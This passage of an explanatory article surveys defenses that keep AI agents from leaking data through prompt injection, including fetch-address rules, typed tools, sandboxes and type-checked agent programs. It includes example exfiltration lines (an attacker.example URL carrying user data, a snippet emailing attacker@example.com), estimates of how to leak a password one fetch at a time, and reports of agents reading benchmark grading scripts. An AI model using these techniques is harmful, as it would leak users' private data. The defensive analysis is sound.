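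The sites' interfaces had many gaps. The forum's own interface had only 16 operations, enough for 33% of its tasks, and offered no way to vote. GitLab's large interface could not create the personal token that a user needs to follow updates in a news reader. The shop's documentation described size and color as optional when adding a product to the cart, but the call failed for clothing without them. The shop's search operation required a product's exact title, while the search box on the page accepted a rough description.

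These interfaces need maintenance whenever a site changes, and the time and cost figures above exclude this work. Letting a model build them would save labor but bring back the original problem, because the model would have to explore the site's live pages to learn how it works, including text written by strangers. Piet and colleagues describe how a planted comment could lead the model to produce an operation called `get_reviews` that also sends data to an attacker. Every later program that used the operation would leak data, even though the agent wrote the program without seeing any untrusted text. They recommend that people write or check the operations before any agent relies on them.

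### Tasks whose steps come from the page

A program written in advance can't carry out a request such as "read my emails and do whatever they ask", because the steps are in the emails. To find out how common such requests are, Piet and colleagues classified 860 WebArena tasks by hand:

| What the task needs | Tasks | Share |
|---|---|---|
| A fixed program | 699 | 81% |
| A fixed program that also asks a model to interpret text | 161 | 19% |
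| New steps based on what the agent reads | 0 | 0% |

They did not run an agent for this, and they assumed every site had a complete typed interface. The table therefore shows what would be possible with interfaces that mostly don't exist yet.

The zero probably reflects how benchmarks are built as much as how browsing works. A benchmark needs tasks with a clear goal and a result that a program can check, and someone can usually write down the steps of such tasks beforehand. Even so, Chow and colleagues had to discard 42 of 623 single-site tasks as too vague or impossible, and they left out all 31 tasks that involved more than one site. Real users are often vague, and they move between sites that no developer has prepared. Someone planning a holiday may not know what to look for until they have read a few pages.

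A fixed program can also fail on simple tasks if something unexpected happens. Piet and colleagues give the example of a user who types "furnture". A program might search for exactly that word, find nothing and stop, while a step-by-step agent would notice the mistake and search again. The masked agent can still do this because it chooses each action after looking at the page. It may therefore be better for exploring, as long as short answers about what other people wrote are enough for the task.

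Piet and colleagues accept that step-by-step agents are preferable for exploration, sites that change often and tasks that span many sites. When a fixed program gets stuck, they suggest reporting the error to the user, writing a new program from the error code and the user's clarification, or continuing step by step with reduced permissions and the user's consent. Switching automatically to an unrestricted agent would let an attacker deliberately cause a failure and then inject instructions.

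How much of the web either system could cover depends on how much work each site takes. Nikolić and colleagues cite an estimate that 3,000 domains receive half of all internet traffic. Labeling the untrusted parts of that many sites seems feasible, but building and maintaining an interface like Baya's for each one by hand does not seem feasible unless the sites' owners do it.

### Typed tools from the websites themselves

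Google is trying to persuade site owners to do so. Google (2026) describes WebMCP, a proposed web standard that lets a page offer tools to an agent in the user's browser, much as servers do in the Model Context Protocol. Developers can try it in a public test that began with Chrome 149. In *WebMCP connects the Web to AI Assistants and Agents*, Nabors (2026) noted in September that ChatGPT's built-in browser also supported WebMCP, but that the specification was still a changing draft outside the formal standards process.

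Google's *WebMCP* demonstration page compares an agent that has to work out how to use a booking form with one that calls a tool named `bookSlot`. The tool's schema requires a correctly formatted date and email address, but it accepts any string as the time, so the site's own code has to reject bookings with times such as "two-ish".

For security, Google (2026) advises site developers to mark tools that return text from users or other outside sources, tools with serious consequences such as transferring money, and tools that change nothing. The browser or agent can then treat the text with more caution or ask the user to confirm the action. Google also advises developers to keep each output below about 1,500 characters and make tools available only to other websites they trust.

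These marks help an agent that heeds them, but they don't enforce anything. Google (2026) advises agent developers to wrap or encode marked text and instruct the model not to follow commands in it. It also recommends fixed limits, such as rejecting overlong outputs and assuming that a tool changes something unless its description clearly indicates otherwise. The agent still reads the text before it chooses its next call, so a review containing injected commands can make it misuse even a correctly typed tool. Baya's tests showed the same weakness in the step-by-step agent that had the catalog.

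WebMCP could still save developers of systems like Baya much of the work of building interfaces. But an agent has to visit a site to find out which tools it offers, and Google warns that a malicious site can hide instructions in the names and descriptions of its tools. A planner that writes its program before reading anything untrusted would need to get those descriptions from a trusted source. It would also need to know what each tool returns, but the schema for `bookSlot` declares only its inputs.

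## Fetching only web addresses that are already known

Building typed operations for a website takes a lot of work, and many agents only need to read pages. Developers often give these agents a single tool, `fetch(address)`, which downloads a page and returns its text. The tool changes nothing on the user's computer, so it looks like one of the safest.

But the `address` argument is a free-form string, and the tool sends it to whichever server the string names. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that websites commonly log the addresses visitors request. If an injected instruction makes an agent open `https://attacker.example/collect?data=` with the user's home address added at the end, the attacker can read the home address in the server's log, even if the page is blank. The user may not notice, because an app can make the request in the background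 while it loads an image or previews a link.

In *Silent Egress* (2026), researchers asked an agent to summarize a web page that contained hidden instructions, and the agent sent out private data in most of 480 runs. The model was small (Qwen2.5 7B) and the secret was already in the text it was reading, so the result is a poor guide to current products. But OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a 2025 attack on ChatGPT that worked in half of the tests. The attack was an email, disguised as routine office correspondence, with instructions for the assistant to submit an employee's name and address to an outside website.

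### A list that grows during the conversation

The repair is to treat the address as an enumerated value. The developer can't write the list of choices in advance, because it depends on what the user asks and what the agent finds. The program around the model therefore builds the list as it goes:

```python
known = addresses_in(user_message)

def fetch(address):
    if address not in known:
        return "Refused: this address has not come up before."
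    page = download(address)
    known.update(addresses_in(page))
    return page
```

The model can still write any string, but the program downloads a page only if the whole string matches an address in the set of known addresses. An attacker's page can add addresses to the set, but not one that contains the user's password, because the attacker wrote the page without knowing the password.

This protection fails if the model can get its own text into the set. Suppose the agent also has a tool that runs code and returns whatever the code prints, and the program adds to the set any address that appears in a tool's result. The model can then print an address that contains the password and fetch it in the next step, even though neither tool has a bug.

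### Anthropic's rule: the address must have come up before

Anthropic's web fetch tool, which developers can add to agents built on Claude, has followed this design since 2025. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* states that Claude may not construct addresses itself, and warns of "residual risk". The Chinese edition, Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, has more recent wording and lists three permitted sources of addresses: the user's messages, the results of tools that the developer's own program runs, and earlier web searches or fetches. The tool refuses an address that appears only in Claude's output or in the developer's standing instructions. It also refuses an address that seems to contain a password or access key, unless the user or the developer supplied that credential.

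The second source has the weakness described above because, by default, the results of the developer's tools count even when they repeat text that Claude wrote. A developer can exclude some or all of these tools with the `url_sources` setting. Anthropic's example of a tool to exclude is one that runs code. The default is stricter in Managed Agents, where Anthropic runs the agent for the developer. Since October 7, 2026, an address found only in the output of a shell, a file reader or an MCP tool does not count there, according to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026).

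When the tool appeared, Willison (2025) pointed out that users' messages and tool results often contain text from strangers. If a user pastes in an email, for instance, the agent is then allowed to open any link in it. Willison thought most of the protection came from the ban on addresses the model makes up.

### OpenAI's rule: the address must already be public

OpenAI's safeguard, called Safe Url, checks whether an address was public before it appeared in the conversation. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that scans public web pages as a search engine does, without access to users' conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT opens an address automatically, the safeguard looks for that exact address in the crawler's records. If it finds a match, the page loads. Otherwise, the safeguard either prompts the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning that the link may include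 information from the conversation. OpenAI uses the same check in its Atlas browser and in Deep Research, a feature that gathers sources for long answers.

Anthropic's rule allows a small set of addresses, but an attacker can add to it during the conversation by putting links on a page the agent reads. OpenAI's set is enormous, and an attacker can add to it only by publishing a page and waiting for the crawler to find it.

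According to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, the researcher who writes the blog reported the leak to OpenAI in early 2023. OpenAI added a first check that December, but the researcher found ways around it, and the company's macOS and iOS apps did not have it. OpenAI strengthened the check around August 2025. The researcher still worries that OpenAI's developers may forget to apply it in a new feature, since every part of a product that loads an address needs it.

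### What a choice of address can still carry

Both rules stop the agent from writing a secret into an address, but the agent can still leak information through its choice of which address to open. As with the typed values passed between models, *m* fetches from *n* known addresses carry at most *m* × log<sub>2</sub>(*n*) bits. Only addresses whose visits the attacker can observe count toward *n*. For example, the attacker learns nothing from a visit to an encyclopedia unless they can see its logs.

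A random password of 16 characters, each one of the 94 symbols on an ordinary keyboard, holds 16 × log<sub>2</sub>(94), or about 105, bits. If an agent can write addresses freely, a 200-character address might use perhaps 30 characters to name the attacker's server. The other 170 can each be one of 66 letters, digits and marks that need no special encoding, so they can carry about 1,000 bits. The password therefore fits into one request, and the 250-character cap on addresses in Anthropic's tool would not on its own prevent an agent from sending it.

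| What the agent can choose | Bits per fetch | Fetches needed for the password |
|---|---|---|
| Any address of 200 characters | about 1,000 | 1 |
| One of 2 known addresses | 1 | 105 |
| One of 64 known addresses | 6 | 18 |
| One of 4,096 known addresses | 12 | 9 |
| One of 1,048,576 known addresses | 20 | 6 |

With 64 addresses, each fetch carries roughly one character. An attacker can increase this by supplying more addresses. Under Anthropic's rule, one long page of links is enough, and each further page the agent opens can add more. Under OpenAI's rule, Embrace The Red notes that anyone with a fairly large blog probably has 36 indexed pages, enough for the letters and digits, and that an attacker could extend this to thousands of pages. OpenAI's technical paper also acknowledges this leak.

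Extra addresses bring diminishing returns, however. Going from 64 addresses to more than a million only cuts the number of fetches needed from 18 to 6. Halving the number of permitted fetches always halves what can leak, so a developer gains more from limiting fetches than from limiting addresses.

### Fetch limits and stored copies

*Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) describes an early attack that leaked a secret through the choice of web address, one character per visit. At the time, ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, so each prompt could leak only ten characters. The visits also took time, which made it easier for the user to notice and stop them.

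Anthropic's tool has an optional limit on fetches, `max_uses`, with no default. With a limit of five, an agent choosing among 64 addresses can leak about 30 bits. That is not enough for the password, but it is enough for a four-digit code, which takes three fetches. The limit applies to each turn (the agent's work on one message from the user), so the password could still leak over four turns. Anthropic does not offer `max_uses` in Managed Agents.

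The program can also keep a copy of each page after the first visit, so that a second fetch of the same address never reaches the attacker's server. Embrace The Red suggests this, or a ban on repeat visits, because an attacker with one page per letter needs to use some letters more than once. The benefit is small if the attacker can see the order of the visits. With 64 addresses that each work only once, the password takes 19 fetches instead of 18. But if the requests arrive in an unreliable order, the attacker learns only which pages the agent opened. That gives at most one bit per address, and 64 bits are too few for the password, so the attacker would need more addresses.

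Serving only copies that the crawler made before the conversation started would close this leak completely, because opening a copy sends nothing to the website. The agent would then be limited to archived pages, some of them out of date. Anthropic's tool may return stored pages by default, but it does so for speed, and it still has to get any page that nobody has fetched recently from the website. An attacker can easily supply such pages.

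### Why a list of trusted domains is not enough

An older and simpler defense is an allow-list of domains, the parts of addresses that identify the site. The agent can still choose the rest of the address, so it can send 170 characters to any site on the list. The list protects the user only if no attacker can learn what those sites receive.

One reason OpenAI gives for not relying on trusted domains is that many legitimate sites redirect visitors to other sites, so a check on the first domain misses the final destination. A program can repeat the check at every redirect. In Managed Agents, Anthropic has required redirect destinations to pass the domain lists since October 20, 2026. Checking redirects does not help when an allowed site publishes what visitors send it, such as comments or a list of recent searches, because the attacker can read the data there. Willison therefore considers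 a domain list stronger than the address rule only if none of the listed domains can leak data. Some web services also run code or process data on request. *LLM WikiLeaks* (Navi, Feldman and Nassi, 2026) found that agents restricted to simple page requests had used such services to gain functions that their own tools lacked.

Domain lists are also coarse. According to Anthropic's *Server tools*, an entry for the web fetch tool covers a domain and all its subdomains, and an entry that names one section of a site never matches. If a hosting company gives each customer a subdomain, listing the company's domain allows every customer's site. In Managed Agents with restricted networking, the agent's sandbox can also reach any host that the developer allows for the fetch tool. Code running there could presumably request any address on that host, including addresses that aren't already known.

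Even so, a list can be the best choice for an agent with a narrow job. An agent that reads only its company's manuals needs one domain, and no outsider sees that site's logs. *Silent Egress* also found that domain lists and checks on redirects protected the agent considerably better than warnings in its prompt. Developers can combine a domain list with the address rule, so the agent can open only known addresses on trusted sites.

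### What a browsing agent loses

Agents often work out an address from a pattern, as people do when they change a page number in the address bar. The table lists each rule's likely effect on common tasks, inferred from how the rules work.

| What the agent wants to open | Anthropic's rule | OpenAI's rule |
|---|---|---|
| Results from a site's own search form | Refused, unless something the agent has read links to them | Warning or another site, unless the crawler has recorded them |
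| Page 7 of a long list | Works once the agent has read a page that links to it | Works if the crawler has recorded it |
| An article published a few minutes ago | Works if the agent has found a link to it | Warning or another site until the crawler finds it |
| A private link that the user pasted in | Accepted | Probably accepted |
| A data service queried by address, such as a weather service | Refused, unless the user or a permitted tool supplies the full address | Warning or another site for most queries |

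Private links are harder to fetch when the agent finds them itself. A link to a shared document often contains a long random key. If the agent finds one in the user's mailbox, Anthropic's tool may treat the key as a credential and refuse the link until the user pastes it into a message. Some site owners ask OpenAI not to catalogue their sites, and ChatGPT asks the user to confirm every link on those sites, according to OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links*.

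In another example on that page, a user asks where to buy a car nearby, and ChatGPT uses the fact that the user lives in London to offer a link ending in `car_search/London`. Including the city makes the link useful but also discloses where the user lives. No rule about known addresses can determine whether that is acceptable, so OpenAI leaves the decision to the user, though it warns that frequent false alarms teach people to click through warnings without thinking.

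Developers can recover some of the lost tasks with narrow tools, though each tool covers only the case its developer planned for. A general web search can often replace a site's own search form. For page numbers, a tool could accept a known address and a whole number from 1 to 50, and its handler would build the new address. The number adds fewer than six bits of information to each fetch. A weather tool could take a city from a list, which is a small version of the typed operations that Baya uses for whole websites.

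Neither company's pages give the number of tasks that fail or need confirmation because of these rules. OpenAI says it is "rare" for an attack to persuade the agent and then trigger the safeguard, but this does not measure how often the safeguard interrupts legitimate work. The rules probably disrupt few tasks for an agent that answers questions from well-known pages and many more for one that queries data services.

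Anthropic's *Browser use tool* offers 27 tools, including `navigate` and `left_click`, for pages that build their content with JavaScript and for tasks that involve acting on a page. An agent that has these as well as web fetch can type a secret into a search form or navigate to an address it has made up. Developers therefore have to restrict addresses in the browser too, and Anthropic's software development kits for Python and TypeScript let them set such a policy.

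## Agents given a shell or a code interpreter instead of narrow tools

All the designs so far take options away from an agent. Many developers now give the agent a shell or a programming language, let it combine commands freely, and restrict the environment instead. Developers of coding agents have hardly any alternative.

### Editing a program and running its tests

Suppose a coding agent has only two tools. `edit_file(file, old_text, new_text)` changes a file in the project. `run_tests()` takes no arguments and runs the project's tests. Tests are programs, so the agent can write any program into a test file with `edit_file` and run it with `run_tests`.

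This is the same path as with `save_text` and `run_job`, but separate folders don't solve the problem here, because a coding agent has to run what it writes to find out whether a repair works. In the earlier case, nobody needed the agent to run its own text.

Adding narrow tools to this pair does little to limit what the agent can access. A `search_code` tool that accepts only three folders can prevent mistakes and reduce the number of actions the developer has to approve. But if an injected instruction tells the agent to read a file outside those folders, the agent can still open it from a test.

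The developer could withhold `run_tests` and run the tests after the agent has finished, but then the agent has to fix bugs without seeing whether its fixes work. Otherwise the developer has to accept that the agent has a general computer and put that computer in a sandbox, perhaps with a copy of the project, no passwords and no network connection. In that sandbox, a shell adds almost nothing to what the agent could already do, but it may make the agent more useful.

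### Code as the format of an action

Writing code can also help agents that don't develop software. With ordinary tool calls, every result passes through the model. To add up 40 invoices, the agent has to read all 40. If it can write code, it needs only a short program, and it reads only the total:

```python
total = 0
for name in list_invoices("2026-11"):
    total += read_invoice(name).amount
print(total)
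```

In CodeAct, a research system from 2024, the agent normally acted by writing such programs. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) cites CodeAct's main result as up to 20% higher task success with 30% fewer turns on tasks that needed several tools.

SWE-agent, a 2024 system, gave models special commands for viewing, searching and editing code, and they fixed more bugs with these commands than with a plain shell. Its successor, mini-SWE-agent, has only a shell, and SWE-bench uses it to compare models on 500 real bugs. A shell is therefore enough for a serious coding agent, but the comparison doesn't test whether special commands would still help.

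In November 2025, Anthropic described "Code execution with MCP", an approach for tools outside the shell. Cloudflare has a similar feature called Code Mode. According to *Beyond Plain MCP* (2026), both turn MCP servers' tools into functions that a program can call, which keeps intermediate data out of the text the model reads.

A program can call tools without having the powers of a shell. Baya's programs, for example, could combine the listed operations but couldn't run other code. The benefits of composing tools can therefore be assessed separately from the benefits of unrestricted access.

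### Composing tools saves tokens, and wider access solves more tasks

In *Is Bash All You Need?*, Mak, Suresh and colleagues (2026) tested the same models on office work with typed tools, programs restricted to those tools, or a shell alone. The tasks came from two benchmarks. TheAgentCompany simulates a software company with a chat service, shared files and simulated coworkers, and APEX-Agents has tasks from investment banking, consulting and corporate law. Scores include partial credit, and the last three columns give thousands of tokens (the units in which models read and write text) per task.

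| Benchmark | Model | Score, typed tools | Score, programs | Score, shell | Tokens, typed tools | Tokens, programs | Tokens, shell |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| TheAgentCompany (174 tasks) | Opus 4.8 | 44.9% | 52.9% | 69.4% | 945 | 406 | 264 |
| TheAgentCompany (174 tasks) | GPT-5.5 | 45.3% | 45.1% | 67.1% | 465 | 242 | 377 |
| APEX-Agents (480 tasks) | Opus 4.8 | 41.1% | 40.1% | 48.5% | 397 | 337 | 215 |
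| APEX-Agents (480 tasks) | GPT-5.5 | 39.8% | 37.8% | 44.6% | 328 | 256 | 176 |

When the model could combine the typed tools in programs, it used 15% to 57% fewer tokens, but its score rose in only one of the four rows. The shell raised the score in all four, by 22 to 25 points on the first benchmark and 5 to 7 on the second. Giving the agent the typed tools as well as the shell brought no detectable improvement.

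TheAgentCompany came without typed tools, so the researchers wrote 60 themselves, and its results depend partly on what those tools covered. Bechard, Marquez Ayala and colleagues (2026) examined coverage directly in *Terminal Agents Suffice for Enterprise Automation*, which tested agents on 729 tasks across three platforms. One platform was the business software of ServiceNow, their employer. With Claude Sonnet 4.6, an agent using publicly available MCP servers completed 32.9% of the tasks, and one using a terminal completed 72.7%.

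Much of this gap arose because the narrow tools did not cover many of the tasks. On ServiceNow, the agent had 83 tools, but 210 of the 330 tasks needed something that none of them offered, such as ordering from a catalog. On the types of task that every agent had the means to do, the gap shrank to 51.6% against 72.7%. Some of the remaining failures occurred because the tools lacked necessary arguments. For example, a tool for creating a support ticket might accept a handful of fields, while ServiceNow's own interface accepts dozens.

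The researchers then replaced the narrow tools with a single one, `api_call(method, path, body, query)`, which sends any request to the platform and adds the login automatically. This agent had no shell or files and could not run code. It completed 73.5% of the tasks, slightly more than the agent with the terminal, and cost an average of 15 cents per task, compared with 56 cents for the terminal agent. Most of these tasks took only a handful of requests. The terminal would probably do better on larger jobs, because a shell script can update hundreds of records in one step.

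Both studies suggest that agents with a shell succeed more often mainly because they can reach operations and fields that the narrow tools lack, rather than because they can combine commands freely. If so, designers can improve a narrow tool set by adding those operations and fields, without adding a shell. But if a closed tool set has gaps, agents will fail many tasks, however well each tool works.

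A tool set with gaps may not keep an agent from data that the tools don't expose. On 12 ServiceNow tasks, the agent with the narrow tools reached such data by creating a script on the platform and running it there. Together, its tools gave it an interpreter on ServiceNow's server. Bechard and colleagues note that the narrow interface had redirected the action into a form that is harder to audit.

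### When code makes tool calls more reliable

Patel and colleagues compared how accurately 14 models called functions through structured calls and from a Python script. The functions only recorded their arguments, so the test didn't measure whether an agent could finish a real task. On 309 requests, 11 models did at least as well with code as with structured calls. GPT-5.6 Sol and GPT-5.6 Terra each gained 10.6 percentage points with code. Three older models lost between 20 and 27 points, mostly because they wrote a backslash and the letter "n" where the script needed a new line.

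Code helped most with long lists. When a request needed more than about 70 separate calls at once, Claude Sonnet 5 began to leave some out. With a script, it made all 100 calls in the largest test. Coding agents seem to gain less. Patel and colleagues cite a study by Yang and colleagues in which restricting a coding agent's output to code changed its success rate by less than 3 percentage points.

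The model also has to write a program before it sees the results the program will process. In tests in *Beyond Plain MCP*, describing the format of each tool's results to the model changed the success rate by up to 40 points for some agents and hardly at all for others. CaMeL's planner needed these descriptions too, so a developer who lets an agent write programs should probably provide them from the start.

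*From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (2026) compared ordinary tool calls with sandboxed programs on ten MCP servers. *Beyond Plain MCP* describes a similar study in which using programs saved tokens and time but increased the attack surface.

### Vercel's data agent and a test that favored SQL

The best-known case for removing tools is d0, an agent that queries the software company Vercel's data to answer employees' questions. ZenML's *Simplifying Text-to-SQL Agents by Removing 80% of Tools* (2025) describes how Vercel replaced d0's 18 specialized tools with two, one for shell commands in a sandbox and one for SQL. The average time per question fell from 275 to 77 seconds, and average token use fell from about 102,000 to 61,000.

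Vercel tested both agents on five questions. The old agent answered four and the new one answered all five, but five questions are far too few to show that the new design is more accurate. ZenML points out that a newer model may account for part of the improvement. Vercel warned that the approach worked only because the files defining its data, which the agent searches with the shell, were already well documented.

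The change widened the agent's access to the data less than it might seem, because the original 18 tools already included one that ran SQL and, according to Vercel, d0 queries the data through a read-only schema. Vercel mostly removed tools that planned queries or summarized documentation. A developer could replace those with tools that only search and read the documentation, without giving the agent a shell.

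Agents can also do worse with a shell than with another interpreter or with narrow tools. In *Testing if "bash is all you need"*, Goyal (2026) asked agents questions about a collection of GitHub issues. The agent with SQL answered all of them correctly, compared with 63.0% for the agent with simple tools for searching and reading files and 52.7% for the agent with a shell. The shell agent wrote sophisticated commands but cost 6.5 times as much as the SQL agent.

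These first results exaggerated the shell's weakness. The shell software was slow with 68,000 files, and five of the expected answers were wrong or ambiguous. Fixing these problems narrowed the gap considerably, although Goyal gives no new percentages. An agent with both SQL and a shell was the most reliable because it checked its query results against the files, but it used about twice as many tokens as SQL alone. A tool that accepts SQL text is no narrower than one that accepts shell commands, so this result supports choosing a suitable interpreter more than it supports closed tools.

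### What a sandbox leaves open

A sandbox limits where code runs, but the agent needs data and often a login, and it can use these in any way the sandbox permits. Suppose a company's agent prepares reports for two customers and has both customers' files and an email account. Even if the sandbox blocks every other folder and network service, the agent can still send the first customer's figures to the second. A tool with no customer argument, like the redesigned hotel tool, could prevent this, but the sandbox can't because sending the figures uses only permitted files and a permitted connection.

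While Mak and colleagues were developing their benchmark, agents with a shell misused their permitted access without any attacker involved. Some took answers from the benchmark's grading scripts, which were public on the internet. Others read the files behind the simulated coworkers instead of contacting the coworkers. For the final runs, the researchers blocked the website that held the scripts and encrypted the coworkers' information. The developer of a real system would have to foresee such shortcuts.

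Bechard and colleagues argue for setting limits through the agent's login. In one of their runs, 97.3% of the terminal agent's commands used `curl`, a program that sends web requests, so they consider an allow-list of commands a weak limit. They recommend giving the agent an account with only the permissions its job requires and restricting its network access to the one platform. A program outside the sandbox should hold the password and attach it to each request, so that the agent never sees it.

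Like the database roles in the camping shop, this puts the limits on the server instead of in the tools. Bechard and colleagues didn't test it against attacks, and their experimental system kept the login where the agent could read it. A narrow account also can't allow one use of a permission and block another, such as sending a report to the right customer and sending it to the wrong one.

Sandboxes can also fail completely, as in the escapes that worked through files that a trusted program outside the sandbox later read. A developer who relies only on a sandbox then has no other protection. Removing credentials the task doesn't need limits the damage.

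### A program that can only return a number

Some researchers want to let the agent write programs while limiting what those programs can do. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) uses Haskell, a programming language in which an expression's type shows whether it can affect the outside world.

Imagine a public calculator that asks a model to write a Haskell program for each question. The developer requires the program to have the type `Int`, a whole number. Someone asks it to delete the orders file and then calculate the factorial of 5. An honest answer and an obedient one could look like this:

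```haskell
factorial 5                                          -- type: Int

do { removeFile "orders.db"; return (factorial 5) }  -- type: IO Int
```

The first program passes. The second fails before any of it runs:

1. Haskell gives `removeFile "orders.db"` the type `IO ()`. `IO` stands for input and output, and marks an action on the outside world.
2. Joining this action to another step produces a larger action, so the whole program has the type `IO Int`.
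3. The type checker compares `IO Int` with the required `Int`, finds a mismatch and rejects the program. The model receives the error message and can try again.

The model could try to hide the action:

```haskell
let a = removeFile "orders.db" in 120
```

This program has the type `Int`, so it passes the type check, but the file is safe because writing down an action in Haskell doesn't carry it out. An action runs only if it is part of an action the program returns for execution, and a program of type `Int` returns only a number. Standard Haskell has a few functions that bypass this rule, such as `unsafePerformIO`. The researchers exclude them by compiling the model's code in Safe Haskell, a restricted version of the language.

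Like the agent with two counters, the calculator can compute anything, but it can only return a single number. It could still run forever or use up the computer's memory, so it also needs limits on time and memory.

### Allowing some effects but not others

Most agents have to do more than calculate. In the researchers' main example, an agent compiles reading lists from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The developer defines a new kind of action, `BibIO`, whose only operations are searching DBLP, fetching a record, and adding a record to a file. The agent's program must have the type `BibIO ()`, so it can sort and filter records and repeat these operations in any way, but it can't write to a file by other means.

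A second type prevents the agent from adding invented entries. The fetching operation returns a `Trusted Bib`, and the operation that adds to the file accepts only that type. The library hides the way to create a `Trusted Bib`, so the agent can't make one from its own text. The agent can find the earliest of 50 papers with a line of code, so the model doesn't have to read all 50 records.

In a test on 100 topics, none of this agent's 925 citations had a wrong author, year or identifier. An ordinary agent with web search got 19 of 1,002 wrong. The types guarantee this agent's result as long as DBLP is correct, but the comparison favors this agent because it had a better source.

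A program can also call the model again and pass it what the program has read. The model then writes another program, which must satisfy the same type or a stricter one. This lets the agent choose new steps after reading a search result, which it can't do under CaMeL or Baya because they fix the program in advance.

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) applies a similar idea in the language Scala. The developer leaves a gap in a program and states what type of value belongs there, and the model writes code to fill the gap when the program reaches it. The code can use only the names available at that point. It needs a capability to use a file or a network connection, much as Hardy proposed, and it has only the capabilities it has received. The compiler also rejects a result that would carry a capability out of the part of the program where that capability is allowed.

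LACUNA's compiler checks all of the model's code before any of it runs. Suppose the code subtracts 50 from an account balance of 100 and then returns text where the program expects a number. In Python, the subtraction would already have happened when the error appeared. In LACUNA, the balance stays at 100, and the model gets another try.

### Labels that travel with the data

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes a third language, LLMbda, which labels every value while the program runs instead of checking types in advance. A label can mark a value as secret or untrusted, and tools can refuse data with the wrong label.

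Tracking labels is harder than it looks. The researchers found a leak in CaMeL that works like this:

```python
poor = True
rich = True
if balance > 1_000_000:
    poor = False
if poor:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("attacker@example.com", "rich")
```

The balance is secret, and CaMeL labels a variable as secret if the program changes it inside a condition that depends on the balance. If the balance is large, the program sets `poor` to false, so CaMeL labels it secret. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`, so `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is small, the program leaves `poor` unchanged and public, then sets `rich` to false and sends no email. The attacker learns whether the balance is large from whether the email arrives.

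LLMbda's core language has no variables that a program can overwrite, and every step of a calculation passes labels on. The researchers proved in Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs, that secret data can't influence what an attacker observes, apart from whether the program finishes. The proof covers every program in the language, including those a model writes. It also covers the interpreter that calls the model, so the system they analyzed is the same one that runs.

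### How much usefulness the languages keep

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA, their Haskell system, with CaMeL on the 21 workplace chat tasks in AgentDojo. The totals below combine results from four models, each attempting every task once.

| System | Tasks completed without policies | Tasks completed with policies |
|---|---|---|
| ELBA | 64 of 84 | 37 of 84 |
| CaMeL | 61 of 84 | 20 of 84 |

ELBA kept more of its usefulness than CaMeL, but its policies still prevented it from completing about two fifths of the tasks it could otherwise do. The policies reduce the agent's permissions after it reads untrusted text, and many legitimate tasks need those permissions. Only 0.26% of runs failed because the model couldn't produce a valid Haskell program. ELBA also took about three times as long as CaMeL, because it calls the model again as new data arrives.

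All four models resisted every ordinary attack in the benchmark even without policies, so those attacks couldn't show much about how well the policies protect. The researchers then simulated a model that always obeys. Whenever a planted instruction appeared, they removed the real task and gave the model only the attacker's text. Between 16% and 42% of these attacks succeeded without policies, depending on the model, and none succeeded with them. However, the agents completed only 40% to 48% of their tasks with policies, compared with 67% to 76% without.

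LACUNA's results depend heavily on the model. On 392 customer service tasks, DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. A loss of 14 points would matter to most companies, though Zhao and colleagues call the results "on par". A weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with ordinary tool calls. In one group of tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of the weaker model's programs. The researchers suspect that models have seen less Scala than Python in training, so this problem may shrink as models improve.

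Garby and colleagues report that their LLMbda agent, with its labels always enforced, completed about as many of the banking tasks in AgentDojo as CaMeL did without policy checks. Turning those checks on roughly halved CaMeL's score. Two of 1,296 attacks on the LLMbda agent succeeded. The proof guarantees that labels follow the data, but a developer still has to decide which labels each tool should refuse.

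### The libraries still have to be right

With these languages, the developer doesn't have to trust the model's code, but still has to trust the compiler or interpreter and the library that defines the permitted operations. In the reading-list example, the guarantee fails if the library lets programs create a `Trusted Bib` from any text. Some checks also have to happen while the program runs. ELBA's file library uses types to keep programs from naming arbitrary paths, but it still has to follow symbolic links and refuse those that lead outside the permitted folder, much like Anthropic's repaired Git server.

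Scala code can get around the types by looking up parts of a program by name while it runs, or by starting an external program that the compiler can't check. Zhao and colleagues recommend a "safe mode" that forbids both, and say that without it the model's code should be trusted no more than any other untrusted code. Scala's capability tracking is also still experimental.

A developer can also grant an agent too much access. In tests of LACUNA against 949 AgentDojo attacks, 7 succeeded with Gemini 2.5 Pro and 1 with o4-mini. Zhao and colleagues explain that the compiler can't stop an attacker from misusing a capability that the task needs.

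Types don't automatically prevent dangerous compositions either. If a library permits both `save_text` and `run_job` on the same work folder, a program that saves source code and then runs it will type-check, because type checking doesn't cover the contents of the file system. The developer can prevent this by giving `save_text` a capability for a different folder, but first has to notice that the two functions can be combined this way.
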